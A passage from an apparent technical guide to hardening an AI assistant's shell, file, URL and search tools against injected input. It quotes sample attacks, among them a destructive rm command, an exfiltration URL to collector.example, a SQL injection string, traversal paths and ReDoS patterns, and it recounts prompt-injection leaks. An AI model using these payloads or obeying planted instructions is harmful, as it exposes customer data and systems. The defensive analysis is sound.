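ShellPlan applies this test before it starts anything, as far as the text allows. The text may not show what an argument like `$REPORTS/*.csv` will become, so ShellPlan repeats the test after expanding the arguments, immediately before it starts each program. This supplies much of the information missing from the string, since the expanded arguments are the ones the program will receive. However, ShellPlan may have to stop partway through a plan because a later argument fails the test. LangSec advises checking all the input before acting on it, but ShellPlan can't follow this advice completely because some of the input doesn't exist until earlier commands have run.

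ShellPlan also restricts where output can be redirected. Under a read-only policy, the only allowed destination is `/dev/null`, which discards everything written to it. If the policy allows writing within the project folder, ShellPlan opens each folder on the path to the destination in turn, rejects any links, and verifies the file before emptying it. In a stress test, another program repeatedly replaced a folder with a link to somewhere else while ShellPlan was writing to it. ShellPlan never wrote outside the project in 1,000 rounds, but 741 of them ended in an error that it did not handle cleanly.

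### What the theorems guarantee

Li states two theorems about this design. The first is about single interpretation. If ShellPlan refuses a command, it starts none of the command's programs and opens none of its output files, though it may run a few fixed, read-only tests of its own while deciding. If it accepts the command, every program it starts directly is either one of those tests or a program in the plan whose expanded arguments have passed the checks. No part of the original string reaches a shell. The proof goes from the smallest parts of the plan to the largest, which is possible because a plan inside a command substitution is always smaller than the plan that contains it.

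The second theorem limits the effects of an accepted plan in which every program has a specification. The plan can start only the programs it contains, ShellPlan's own tests, and helper programs named in trusted settings. It can write only to permitted redirection targets, apart from temporary files that `sort` creates, an index that Git refreshes, and anything the trusted helpers write.

The theorem about effects depends on two assumptions:

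- **The computer outside the project is trustworthy.** The attacker controls the text that the agent reads and the files in the project folder, but not the environment variables, the system's settings or the installed programs.
- **The utilities behave as their specifications describe.** For example, `grep` writes no files when its arguments are in its permitted set.

The theorem depends mainly on the assumption about utilities. It helps by reducing a question about any accepted command to questions about 20 programs, but people still have to answer those by reading manuals and testing. In Li's tests of 1,213 options, ShellPlan always matched the program on whether an option takes the next word as its value. In 765 tests of Git with permitted settings, Git started no unexpected program. These results support the assumption for the tested versions, but an update to a utility could change them.

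The theorem also doesn't cover reading, since Li leaves out attacks that read files outside the project through an approved command. This is a large omission for the invoicing assistant, because a customer list that `cat` prints goes back to the model, which may then send it out through `fetch_page`. The theorem also excludes programs without specifications, such as the test runner `pytest`. When Li allowed `pytest` in a replay of recorded agent sessions, 44 of 398 approved commands broke the read-only policy, and all 44 were `pytest` runs. None of the 348 commands that used only specified programs broke the policy, except when Git refreshed its index.

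The preprint contains sketches of the proofs. Li plans to release the full proofs and the code after the companies have had time to fix the flaws in their checkers.

### What ShellPlan blocks and what it costs

ShellPlan admitted none of the 4,174 test commands with effects that a read-only policy forbids. These commands don't represent 4,174 different attacks, because 2,685 of them came from automated variation and Li didn't remove duplicates between the six collections. A checker that refused everything would also have admitted none, so the results for harmless commands matter too. In one collection, ShellPlan refused 12 of 161 read-only commands and admitted none of the 316 commands that did more than read.

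The program's implementation also fell short of its design. Li's audits of two earlier versions found 14 causes of security faults, and an audit of the final version found one more, in which the write check did not recognize an unusual arrangement of links inside a project.

Li then tested ten models with and without protection on the same nine tasks containing attacks and ten ordinary tasks. Nobody was available to approve a refused command, but a model could try another one.

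| | Without protection | With ShellPlan |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded | 62 of 90 | 0 of 90 |
| Ordinary tasks completed | 93 of 100 | 74 of 100 |
| by six leading models | 60 of 60 | 56 of 60 |
| by four smaller models | 33 of 40 | 18 of 40 |

The loss of 19 ordinary tasks exaggerates ShellPlan's drawbacks in one respect. Four of the ten tasks deliberately asked for shell features that ShellPlan does not support, and these account for 15 of the 19 losses. The leading models usually found another way to write the command, while the smaller ones often gave up or ran out of turns.

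ShellPlan did less well on recorded sessions of coding agents. In 48 sessions, it admitted 343 of 456 read-only steps, or 75%. In another 12 sessions, it admitted none of 108, because the agent began every command with `cd`, which changes the current folder and which ShellPlan doesn't support. Across both sets, `cd` and `nl`, a program that numbers lines, caused 198 of the 221 refusals, so supporting these two commands could remove most of them. ShellPlan's limits are more basic on a collection of 1,523 shell commands that people had written for many purposes, of which it admitted 28.5%.

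Because ShellPlan runs the plan without a shell, it must also imitate Bash correctly. Its output matched Bash's exactly in all 343 comparisons on the first set of sessions. On the larger collection, one harmless command printed an incomplete result because ShellPlan didn't pass a program's output to a command substitution as Bash does. Incorrect output is less serious than an unauthorized deletion, but a model that relies on it may draw the wrong conclusion.

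### CARE: scoring how dangerous a command looks

Developers who want `run_command` to accept most ordinary commands may prefer a checker that looks for signs of danger. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, July 2026) combines fixed rules with a language model that decides doubtful cases.

CARE first rewrites the command in a standard form without running it, for example by removing unnecessary quotation marks. It then gives the command four scores between 0 and 1. They depend on the type of program, the files it would touch, its resemblance to known attack patterns, and the structure of the command. The total is

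score = 0.3 × program + 0.3 × files + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

CARE approves a command that scores below 0.15 and refuses one that scores 0.35 or more. A command that scores 0.6 for its program and zero for the rest totals 0.18, which is between the two thresholds. CARE refuses a command in this range if one of the individual signs is strong enough, and otherwise asks the model, which has instructions to refuse when uncertain. Most commands never reach the model, which judged 23 of 549 in the main test.

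CARE caught 167 of the 220 dangerous commands in that test (75.9%) and wrongly refused three of the 329 safe ones. Without the model, the rules caught the same number but wrongly refused six, so the model's only contribution was to allow three harmless file transfers that the rules would have refused.

The model made things worse on a harder test. Liu and colleagues had a language model write 600 commands in response to harmful requests, ran them in a sandbox, and counted those that passed the checker and ran successfully.

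| Protection | Harmful commands that passed and ran |
|---|---|
| none | 449 (74.83%) |
| CARE's rules only | 224 (37.33%) |
| CARE's rules and the model | 315 (52.50%) |

The judge model approved 91 commands that would otherwise have been refused and that then ran successfully. The same Qwen model also wrote the attacks, and Liu and colleagues suggest that it approved them because they were phrased the way it phrases things. They did not test a judge from a different model family, so this explanation is uncertain. Whatever the cause, a developer who expects attacks may prefer to keep the rules and leave out the judge.

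The results also depend on the thresholds the developer sets. Lowering the approval threshold from 0.15 to 0.10 raised the share of dangerous commands that the rules caught from 75.9% to 96.8%, but it also raised the share of safe commands refused from 1.8% to 23.1%. Liu and colleagues calculate that if 100 of every 10,000 commands were dangerous, CARE at its default setting would stop about 76 of them, miss 24, and refuse about 90 harmless commands.

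CARE interferes with ordinary work much less than ShellPlan. In a test of 300 everyday tasks, a model completed 57.0% with CARE and 57.3% without protection. The two preprints used different tasks, models and attacks, so their percentages are not directly comparable. CARE accepts any command that doesn't look dangerous, while ShellPlan accepts only commands it can account for. CARE passes the approved command to a shell, so it still depends on interpreting the command as the shell does. It judges each command alone, so it may miss a harmful sequence whose individual steps look harmless. Liu and colleagues say it only partly reduces risk and should be used with a sandbox.

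### What no checker can decide

Better rules and specifications would correct many of these errors, but they can't eliminate every error. According to Rice's theorem, which the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, no algorithm can decide correctly, for every program, whether what the program computes has a given non-trivial property. A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others don't. If a program's changes to files count as part of its result, the theorem applies to questions such as "Does this command ever delete the invoices?"

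The argument for that question is short. Suppose somebody had a checker that always answered it correctly. Take any program that only calculates, call it `prog`, and ask the checker about this command:

```sh
prog > /dev/null; rm invoices.db
```

The shell runs `rm`, which deletes a file, only if `prog` finishes. A checker that could always determine whether the command deletes the invoices could therefore also determine whether any such `prog` finishes. This is the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can solve it, so the checker cannot exist.

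The theorem rules out a checker that always gives an answer, accepts every harmless command and refuses every harmful one. A checker can still judge many individual commands. For example, `ls` deletes nothing if the copy of `ls` is trusted. The theorem also allows a checker to answer "cannot tell" and refuse the command. ShellPlan refuses many harmless commands to keep harmful ones out. CARE accepts some harmful commands and refuses some harmless ones.

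A real computer has limited memory and therefore a finite number of states, so the theorem doesn't strictly apply to it, but there are far too many states to search. A time limit helps more. If the shell stops every command after a minute, running a command in a simulated environment can show what it does in that minute. But the result holds only for the files, variables and network replies in the simulation. The command can behave differently when it runs for real, for instance because a web server sends it different text.

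Missing information and Rice's theorem are separate obstacles. A checker needs only the value of `FILE` to judge `rm $FILE`, but no general method can judge arbitrary Python scripts, even with a complete copy of the computer's state, because it would have to predict what each script computes. Most of ShellPlan's refusals occur because its author hasn't added a feature, not because of the theorem. The theorem becomes relevant when a list of permitted programs includes `python`, `awk`, `make` or anything else that runs code of the caller's choosing. A specification of such a program's options is little help in predicting what it will do, so ShellPlan refuses interpreters by default.

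The operating system can refuse a deletion when a program attempts it, so it doesn't have to predict the deletion. A sandbox uses this ability and can protect the invoices even from a script that no checker could have judged in advance.

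## Why can a well-formed path, URL or search pattern still do harm?

A checker that checks only the spelling of a path, URL or search pattern can miss ways the string could do harm. What a path or URL leads to depends on the file system or the network at the moment it is used, and a very short search pattern can make the engine that runs it do an enormous amount of work. A developer may worry less about the assistant's `read_file`, `fetch_page` and `search_notes` tools than about `run_command`, because those three run no command that the model wrote.

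### Paths that lead out of the folder

Suppose the developer wants `read_file` to return only files in `/data/reports`, and the handler adds the model's argument to the end of the folder's name:

```python
open("/data/reports/" + path)
```

When a tool adds its argument to `/data/reports/`, `march.pdf` works as intended, but `../invoices.db` produces the path `/data/reports/../invoices.db`. Two dots in a path stand for the folder above, so the operating system opens `/data/invoices.db`. This is called path traversal. Separately, Python's function for joining paths, `os.path.join`, discards the first path if the second begins with a slash, so the argument `/etc/hostname` leads to a system file.

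A rule against two consecutive dots would still allow `/etc/hostname`, but it would reject the legal file name `march..final.pdf`. Windows also reserves some names. For example, `CONOUT$` refers to the console whatever folder precedes it (Neil 2025, *Traversal-resistant file APIs*, a post for Go developers). Go's `filepath.IsLocal` function combines such rules. It rejects paths that are empty, are absolute or lead outside their starting folder, and on Windows it also rejects reserved names. Neil thinks such a check may be enough if no attacker can change the file system.

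Many handlers resolve any `..` in a path and then check whether the result begins with `/data/reports`. The argument `../reports-old/2019.pdf` passes this check because it resolves to `/data/reports-old/2019.pdf`, which begins with the same characters but is in a different folder. The MCP project's own file server had a flaw of this type until July 2025. According to GitLab's vulnerability database entry *CVE-2025-53110* (2025), it could give access to unintended files whose path shared a prefix with a permitted folder. Comparing paths folder by folder, or at least including the final slash in the comparison, prevents this.

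The same server had a second flaw, which comparing strings could not have caught. A symbolic link is an entry in a folder that contains another path, and the operating system follows it automatically. If a link called `latest` in a firm's reports folder points to `/home`, a path through it contains no dots and begins with the right folder, but leads outside it. GitLab's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) records that links inside permitted folders could expose files outside them. Release 2025.7.1 fixed both flaws.

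### Why resolving the path first leaves a gap

The usual advice is to canonicalize a path before checking it, which means following every link and removing every pair of dots until one plain, absolute path remains. In Python, the handler becomes:

```python
real = os.path.realpath("/data/reports/" + path)
if os.path.commonpath([real, "/data/reports"]) != "/data/reports":
    raise PermissionError(path)
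return open(real).read()
```

This handles everything described so far, provided `/data/reports` is not itself a link. `realpath` follows links, and `commonpath` compares whole folder names. The handler also opens the same path it checked, as He and colleagues advised after the flaw in Anthropic's Git server.

However, `real` is still only a string. When the handler calls `open`, the operating system looks up each folder again from the top of the file system. If another program has replaced one of those folders with a link since the check, `open` follows the link. Programmers call this a race between the time of check and the time of use. Neil shows the same fault in Go code that resolves a path, checks it and then opens it. This can also happen without a link. If somebody moves a folder to a higher level while the operating system is following a path with several `..` parts, the same number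 of upward steps can lead too far.

An attacker needs some way to change the folder, and Neil gives two ordinary ones. A program that unpacks an archive may create a link from the archive, and software that runs untrusted code in a container may let the code write to part of the disk. Agents often resemble the container case. Suppose `run_command` works in a sandbox that shares the reports folder, while the handler of `read_file` runs outside with access to the whole disk. A command in the sandbox cannot read `/data/invoices.db`, but it can create a link to that path and keep swapping the link with a normal folder until a call to `read_file` arrives at the right moment. The handler then acts as a confused deputy and reads the file for the command.

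### Opening files relative to a directory

A better method is to check the path and open the file in one operation. On Unix systems, a program that opens a directory receives a file descriptor, a number that refers to that directory even if somebody renames it. The system call `openat` opens a file relative to this descriptor, so the handler doesn't have to name `/data/reports` every time.

Plain `openat` does not confine the path, though. As the proposal for Go's version of the feature notes, it permits absolute paths, paths that climb out of the directory, and links that lead out. Linux 5.6 added a stricter call, `openat2`, which the Linux manual's *openat2(2)* describes as a way for trusted programs to restrict how the system resolves untrusted paths. Two of its options confine a path to a directory. They differ in what happens when the path tries to leave:

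| Path from the model | `RESOLVE_BENEATH` | `RESOLVE_IN_ROOT` |
|---|---|---|
| `march.pdf` | opens the file | opens the file |
| `2025/../march.pdf` | opens the file | opens the file |
| `../invoices.db` | error | looks for `invoices.db` in the reports folder |
| `/etc/hostname` | error | looks for `etc/hostname` in the reports folder |
| a link to `/home` | error | looks for `home` in the reports folder |

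The first option seems better for `read_file` because the model learns that the path was wrong, whereas the second may open a different file from the one the path appears to name.

The kernel, the core of the operating system, enforces the restriction while it follows the path, so another program cannot insert a link between the check and the file's use. If something moves at the same moment and the kernel cannot confirm that a `..` stayed inside the allowed directory, the call fails with an error and the program may try again. According to the Linux manual, FreeBSD's earlier equivalent had a bug that made it effectively insecure, and FreeBSD 13 replaced it with one modelled on Linux's.

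Since version 1.24, Go has offered the same protection as a library type, `os.Root`. A handler can use it in one line:

```go
f, err := os.OpenInRoot("/data/reports", path)
```

Go's library works on several operating systems. On Unix it uses the `openat` family of calls and does part of the checking itself, and that checking has had bugs. In an early version, a path ending in `../` could open the parent directory, but not the files in it, according to the US National Vulnerability Database's entry *CVE-2025-22873*. OSV's *GO-2026-4864* (2026) describes a race in the method that changes a file's permissions, which arose because Linux silently ignored an option not to follow links.

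The most serious of the three became public in July 2026. Coopersmith (2026) forwarded the Go team's announcement of the repaired releases to a security mailing list. If a path ended in a slash and its last part was a link, `os.Root` followed the link out of the directory. The library used a Unix option that prevents following a link at the end of a path, but that option has no effect when a slash comes after the link. Go's *Vulnerability Report* (2026) lists every version before 1.25.12 as affected, along with early releases of 1.26 and a test release of 1.27.

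These bugs are a reason to keep Go up to date, but they don't make the older method any better, because checking a path first and opening it later inherently creates the race. A developer on Linux can also call `openat2` directly, which leaves less room for bugs in Go's library, but the C library has no wrapper for it, so the program has to make the system call by number.

Neither `os.Root` nor `openat2` blocks every way to reach files outside a directory. According to comments in Go's source code, `os.Root` does not block access to other file systems mounted inside the directory, to the special files in Linux's `/proc` folder, or to device files. Neil explains that the design guards against what ordinary users can create, such as links, and that mounting a file system requires administrator rights. `openat2` has an option that forbids crossing into another file system, and its manual recommends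 explicitly setting an option to block the special links in `/proc`. Both methods allow hard links, because a hard link is a second name for the same file and has no path to follow.

The method also doesn't limit users to the reports they should see. If the folder contains every customer's reports, `competitor/march.pdf` is a valid path inside it. The handler has to open a directory that belongs to the logged-in user, just as `find_invoices` needed a condition taken from the login session.

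### Which computer does a URL name?

A well-formed URL passed to `fetch_page` can do similar harm, because the server that runs the tool usually sits inside the firm's network and can reach computers that outsiders cannot. One might be an accounts system at `10.0.0.5` that accepts any request from inside the network. On many cloud platforms, a service at `169.254.169.254` gives programs on the same machine temporary passwords for the owner's account, although newer versions require an extra step. If a supplier's e-mail leads the model to fetch such an address, the server makes the request on the supplier's behalf. This is called server-side request forgery, and Padilla's program looked for it on live MCP servers.

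Checking that a URL begins with `https://supplier.example` doesn't guarantee that the request goes to that host. In `https://supplier.example@other.example/`, `supplier.example` is a user name, and the request goes to `other.example`.

The handler should therefore parse the URL and look at the host, the part that names the computer. But a checker and a network client that use different parsers can find different hosts in the same string:

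```
https://supplier.example\@other.example/
```

Two parsers can find different hosts in `https://supplier.example\@other.example/`. Browsers follow the WHATWG URL Standard, which treats a backslash in a web address as a slash, so they read `supplier.example` as the host and the rest as a path. The older standard, RFC 3986, does not allow a backslash in a URL. A parser that follows its structure without rejecting the illegal character reads everything between `//` and `@` as a user name and `other.example` as the host. If the checker uses the first kind of parser and the client uses the second, the checker approves one computer and the client contacts another. LangSec calls this a parse tree differential.

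Even when both parsers agree on the host name, the domain's owner chooses which address it points to. The domain name system (DNS) translates names into numerical addresses, so the owner of `other.example` can make `files.other.example` point to `10.0.0.5`, a private address. Some clients also accept unusual spellings of an address. `http://2130706433/` can mean `127.0.0.1`, the server's own machine, because an IPv4 address is a 32-bit number and 2130706433 is the decimal form of this one. A blocklist of spellings will probably be incomplete, for the reason Andersen and Cohen gave in 1996.

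A handler can look up the hostname, find a harmless public address and approve the call. If the network library then looks up the name again, the owner's DNS server can return a different address. This attack, called DNS rebinding, exploits the same gap between check and use as the swapped folder in `read_file`. An approved URL may also lead to an unchecked one through a redirect, because a web server can send the client to a new URL and most clients follow it automatically.

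The remedy is to do each step once, in order, and carry its result into the next:

```python
def fetch_page(url):
    for hop in range(5):                       # follow at most four redirects
        parts = parse(url)                     # the only parser in the tool
        require(parts.scheme == "https")
        addresses = resolve(parts.host)        # the only name lookup
        require(all(is_public(a) for a in addresses))
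        reply = request(parts, connect_to=addresses[0])
        if not reply.is_redirect:
            return reply.body
        url = join(url, reply.location)        # check the new URL from the top
    raise TooManyRedirects(url)
```

The tool parses the URL once and builds the request from the parsed pieces, so no other parser sees the original string. It allows only `https`, because some clients also accept URLs such as `file:///data/invoices.db`, which would let `fetch_page` read local files. It looks up the host once and rejects the call unless every address it receives is public. This check uses the numeric addresses, so it doesn't matter how an address was written in the URL. The tool then connects to the address it tested, but it still has to use the host's name when checking the server's security certificate, or the connection will fail. It repeats all these steps for each redirect.

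Many network libraries make the `connect_to` step awkward because they take a name and look it up themselves. Go's library lets a developer register a function that receives the actual address just before each connection, including those for redirects, and can refuse the connection. If the server sends its traffic through a proxy, the proxy does the lookup, so the address check belongs there.

A firewall adds a second layer of protection. If the computer that runs `fetch_page` has no route to the accounts system, a mistake in the handler cannot create one. Like the read-only database role, this limit holds whatever string the model writes.

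### A URL also sends data out

The checks above keep `fetch_page` away from internal computers. They do nothing about a request to an outside computer that carries the firm's data with it. A client sends the path and the query of a URL to the web server, and web servers commonly record them. If a hidden instruction in a supplier's e-mail persuades the model to fetch

```
https://collector.example/log?customer=OBrien&owed=4200
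```

then whoever runs `collector.example` learns what Ms O'Brien owes. The host is public, the URL follows the grammar exactly, and it makes no difference what page comes back. The user may not notice, since an application may fetch a URL merely to display an image or a preview.

A DNS lookup alone can leak data. When the handler looks up `obrien-4200.collector.example`, the request eventually carries the data in the hostname to a server that belongs to the owner of `collector.example`. The line `resolve(parts.host)` in the code above would therefore leak the data even if the next line rejected the address. A tool that handles private information has to decide whether a host is acceptable before looking it up.

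Fetching a URL can also change something. Under the rules of HTTP, a GET request should have no side effects, but many sites send e-mails with links that confirm an order or cancel a subscription as soon as someone opens them. If the model calls `fetch_page` on such a link, it triggers the same action.

### Which URLs OpenAI and Anthropic let their agents fetch

Both companies restrict URLs by where they came from, so they don't have to judge what a URL's text might contain. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains why a list of trusted sites is not enough. Many reputable sites have pages that redirect visitors, so a request to a trusted address can end up at an attacker's. Strict lists also produce frequent warnings, and people learn to click through them.

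OpenAI instead uses an index of the public web, which its crawler builds without access to anybody's conversations. ChatGPT may fetch a URL automatically if that exact URL is in the index. OpenAI reasons that a URL that was already public independently of the conversation is much less likely to contain the user's secrets. The address with Ms O'Brien's balance would not be in the index. For any other URL, the agent has to try a different site, or the user sees a warning and decides whether to proceed. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a related mechanism that detects when information from a conversation is about to go to a third party, then either blocks the transfer or shows the user what would be sent. This mechanism covers searches in the Deep Research feature as well as page visits.

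Anthropic's web fetch tool checks whether the URL has already appeared in the conversation. When the tool launched in September 2025, Willison (2025) hoped it would accept only URLs from the user's own messages, but found the rule was looser. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, it also accepted URLs from search results, the developer's own tools and pages it had fetched earlier. The model could not construct a URL, so it could not put the balance in the query. The tool also rejected URLs longer than 250 characters. Anthropic still warned of a remaining risk and advised developers worried about leaks to limit the number of fetches, restrict the tool to known domains, or switch it off.

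The permission to follow links in fetched pages could be used to leak private data. In July, Willison (2026) reported that Ayush Paul had built a website that got Claude to reveal a user's name, home city and employer through the links it followed. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it has since stopped the tool from following links that appear only in pages it fetched.

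OpenAI's rule has a similar limit. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security blog, calls the index a significant improvement but notes that small leaks remain possible, as OpenAI's own paper acknowledges. The reason applies to any list of permitted URLs. If an agent can choose among *k* addresses and makes *m* requests, its choices can convey about

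*m* × log<sub>2</sub> *k* bits

to somebody who sees them all. With 1,000 addresses and 20 requests, that is roughly 200 bits, or 25 characters of plain text, which is enough for a name and a town. With two requests it is 20 bits. A list therefore slows a leak down, and a limit on the number of requests matters as much as the list. The blog's author also suggests that an agent should not request the same URL twice in a session, or that the software should answer the second request from a stored copy.

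OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people with sensitive data, goes further. According to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, it limits browsing to stored copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's own network. This prevents browsing from leaking data, but pages may be outdated or missing. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* adds that planted instructions in a stored page or uploaded file can still affect the answer, that connected apps can still leak data, and that the setting doesn't change network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

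The developer of the invoicing assistant has no index of the web, but probably doesn't need one. `fetch_page` could accept only URLs that the user typed, and ask the user about any others. If the assistant always fetches from the same few suppliers, a list of their hosts works reasonably well, as long as the tool also checks every redirect against it. Suppliers on the list can still receive data in a URL's query string, so the list protects only against hosts that aren't on it.

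### How a short pattern can keep an engine busy for months

`search_notes` passes its argument to a regular-expression engine. Most engines in everyday programming languages work by backtracking. They try one way of matching the pattern, and if it fails, they return to the last choice and try another. The textbook example of what can go wrong is

```
^(a+)+$
```

The pattern `^(a+)+$` matches text made up only of a's, which a person can check at a glance. The `^` and `$` mark the start and end of the text, `a+` matches one or more a's, and `(a+)+` matches one or more such groups.

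Given `aaa`, the engine puts all three letters in one group, reaches the end and reports a match. Given `aaab`, it reaches the b and fails. It can't yet conclude that there is no match, because a different grouping might have worked, so it tries them in turn. With a bar between groups, the attempts are:

```
aaa    aa|a    aa    a|aa    a|a|a    a|a    a
```

After every attempt, the engine finds that it is not at the end of the text. Four of the seven attempts cover all three a's. In general, *n* letters have *n* − 1 gaps between them, and each gap either separates two groups or doesn't, which gives 2<sup>*n*−1</sup> groupings. The attempts that cover only some of the letters bring the total to 2<sup>*n*</sup> − 1. One more letter doubles the work. If an engine tries 100 million groupings a second, the full groupings alone take this long:

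| Letters before the b | Groupings | Time |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | about 520,000 | 5 thousandths of a second |
| 30 | about 540 million | 5 seconds |
| 40 | about 550 billion | an hour and a half |
| 50 | about 560 trillion | 65 days |

Some engines recognize this pattern and avoid the work, but other patterns with the same fault are harder to spot. A model asked to find notes that consist only of words might write `^(\w+\s?)+$`, where `\w` is a letter, digit or underscore and `\s?` is an optional space. Because the space is optional, the engine can split a single long word into groups just as it split the a's. A note containing only a 40-character payment reference and a full stop could then occupy the server for hours, even if nobody attacked it. An attacker could also cause this deliberately by sending the firm a suitable message and a request to search for it.

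A pattern can cause serious trouble even if its matching time doesn't grow exponentially. On 2 July 2019, Cloudflare, which protects and speeds up many websites, sent a new firewall rule to all its servers at once. The rule contained a regular expression with two neighbouring pieces that could each match any text, so the engine tried the different ways of dividing a request between them, and the work grew much faster than the length of the request. According to the company's published account, processors that handled web traffic reached full load around the world, traffic fell by 82% at the worst point, and the outage lasted 27 minutes. This happened even though the rule was in a test mode that blocked nobody. Some weeks earlier, engineers had accidentally removed a safeguard against excessive processor use. Cloudflare's staff had written and tested the pattern, whereas `search_notes` runs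 patterns that nobody has seen before.

### Engines that finish in linear time

Ken Thompson published a method in 1968 that avoids the problem. The engine reads the text once, from left to right, and keeps a set of the positions in the pattern where it could be after each character. For `^(a+)+$`, every grouping of the first thirty a's ends at the same position, just after the `a` in the pattern, where the engine can continue the group, start a new one or stop. A backtracking engine visits that position hundreds of millions of times, while Thompson's method stores it once in the set. The b that follows can't be matched from any position in the set, so the engine reports no match. If the pattern has *m* positions and the text has *n* characters, the work is at most proportional to *m* × *n*. Google's RE2 library, Go's standard library and the main regular-expression library for Rust all guarantee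 this, and Cloudflare announced after its outage that it would move to an engine of this type.

These engines leave out backreferences, which match whatever an earlier group matched. For example, `(\w+) \1` finds a word typed twice in a row. A set of positions doesn't record which word the group matched, and Alfred Aho showed that matching patterns with backreferences is NP-complete in general, so nobody knows a fast method that handles all of them. The engines also leave out lookahead, as in `invoice(?! paid)`, which finds "invoice" only where " paid" does not follow. This is a small loss for a tool that searches a firm's notes. The engine rejects such a pattern with an error before searching, and the model can write a simpler one.

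RE2's guarantee covers a single search, and the time it allows grows in proportion to the size of the pattern. A pattern such as `(a{1000}){1000}` expands to a million positions, so RE2 limits the number of repetitions in a pattern. Finding every match in a text can still take time that grows with the square of the text's length, because the engine may read to the end of the text before it settles on each short match. `search_notes` therefore also needs limits on pattern length and the amount of text, and preferably on time.

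If the developer has to keep a backtracking engine, the time limit becomes the main defence, but it may be hard to apply. Python's standard `re` module has no time limit, and a search blocks the program's other threads, so a timer in the same program may never run. The handler has to run the search in a separate process and stop that process from outside. Developers who use regular expressions to check other arguments face the same problem, although they write the pattern and the model supplies the text.

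A search can also return too much, even with a fast engine. The pattern `.*` runs quickly and matches every note, just as `%` matched every customer in a LIKE query. `search_notes` should search only the notes that the user may read and limit how many it returns.

The developer may not need patterns. Most people who search their notes want a word or a name, so the tool could take plain text and search for exactly that. A search for `O'Brien.pdf` would then no longer find `O'Brien-pdf`, and the engine would have no alternatives to backtrack through. If users sometimes need to search for several words, the tool could accept a list and return the notes that contain any of them.

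## How much can allowlists and refinement types say about a string?

A developer can keep an interpreter from parsing an argument, as in a plain-text `search_notes`, and can also limit which strings reach the interpreter. The options range from a bare "string" in the schema to a handler that receives no text from the model.

| Declaration | Example | What it guarantees | Who enforces it | What still gets through |
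|---|---|---|---|---|
| bare string | `customer` | the value is text | schema validator | any text |
| enumeration | `sort_by` is `due_date`, `newest` or `amount` | one of three known values | validator or handler | the wrong one of the three |
| length and pattern | an invoice number of one to eight digits | text of that shape | validator or handler | somebody else's invoice number |
| distinct type | `InvoiceNumber`, which only one checking function creates | the function accepted the value | the function, then the type checker | whatever the function wrongly accepts |
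| refinement type | text for which a stated condition holds | the condition, wherever the program uses the value | type checker, with run-time tests | a value that meets a badly chosen condition |
| parsed structure | a year and a month instead of a path | no text from the model reaches the interpreter | parser and type checker | the wrong month |

### Enumerations, lengths and patterns

Some checkers test a string argument's type but not its contents. The validator in *Try, Check and Retry* (2026), a method for improving tool calls in long prompts, checks that the tool exists, that the argument names match, and that each value has its declared type. This catches invented tools and arguments, but it accepts any text as a customer's name.

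An enumeration is the strictest allowlist. If the schema lists the three sort keys, the developer can read and test every query that `sort_by` can produce. If the client skips validation, the handler's own table of sort keys still enforces the list. But an enumeration suits only a short list that the developer knows in advance. An MCP server could generate a list of customers from the database, but ten thousand names would fill much of the model's prompt and reveal every customer to anyone who could get the model to repeat the list.

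A pattern can describe far more strings than a list can. Suppose `find_invoices` also accepted an invoice number:

```json
"number": { "type": "string", "pattern": "^[0-9]{1,8}$" }
```

This pattern allows 111,111,110 strings, none of which contains an apostrophe, a space, a hyphen or a slash. JSON Schema looks for a match anywhere in the text, so without `^` and `$` the pattern would accept `' OR '1'='1`, which contains a digit. In Python, `$` also matches just before a newline at the end of the text, so a validator built on the search function accepts `42` followed by a newline, the character missing from the phf script's list. Python's `re.fullmatch` avoids both problems.

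Patterns work badly for names. `^[A-Za-z .'-]{1,80}$` rejects Müller, 3M and every name in Greek letters, but it has to allow the apostrophe in O'Brien. A length limit and a ban on control characters can reject obviously invalid input, but the handler still has to bind the name as a parameter.

### A type that only a checking function can create

After the validator accepts an invoice number, the handler receives an ordinary string, and nothing in the program records the check. A function further down can't tell whether its argument passed. The developer can record it by giving checked values a type of their own:

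```python
@dataclass(frozen=True)
class InvoiceNumber:
    digits: str
    def __post_init__(self):
        if not re.fullmatch("[0-9]{1,8}", self.digits):
            raise ValueError("expected one to eight digits")

def load_invoice(number: InvoiceNumber) -> Invoice: ...
```

Python runs the check whenever the program creates an `InvoiceNumber`, and a type checker reports an error if a programmer passes a plain string to `load_invoice`. But Python's JSON parser returns values of type `Any`, which type checkers accept everywhere, so the developer has to declare the incoming argument as a string before the type checker can detect a missing conversion.

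The guarantee also depends on preventing code from creating the value without the check. In TypeScript, programmers often use a branded type, which is an ordinary string with a label that only the compiler sees. Any programmer can attach that label without running a check. Rust lets a module's author make the constructor private, so code outside the module must call the checking function.

Distinct types also catch arguments in the wrong order. *SafeStrings Representing Strings as Structured Data* (Kelly, Marron and colleagues, 2019) repeats an example in which a function expects a company's identifier and then a user's, and a caller swaps them. The compiler accepts the call because both are strings, but it would reject the call if each identifier had its own type.

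### What a refinement type adds

To the type checker, `InvoiceNumber` is only a name, and it knows nothing about digits. A refinement type includes the condition itself. The usual notation is

{*x* : *B* | *p*}

where *B* is a basic type such as String and *p* is a condition on *x*. The type of invoice numbers is {*x* : String | *x* consists of one to eight digits}.

Knowles (2014), in *Executable Refinement Types*, defines which expressions belong to such a type. An expression *e* belongs to {*x* : *B* | *p*} if it has the basic type *B* and, for every constant *k*,

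if *e* evaluates to *k*, then *p* with *k* in place of *x* evaluates to true.

An expression that never finishes belongs to every refinement of its basic type, because it never produces a constant that could fail the condition. A refinement type therefore restricts what an expression can return but doesn't guarantee that it returns.

The condition lets a type checker compare types. {*x* : *B* | *p*} is a subtype of {*x* : *B* | *q*} if *p* implies *q* for every *x*, and a function that accepts a type also accepts its subtypes. Code that holds a number of up to eight digits can therefore pass it, without another test, to a function that accepts up to twelve. To pass a number of up to twelve digits to a function that accepts only eight, the programmer has to test the value or prove that it is short enough.

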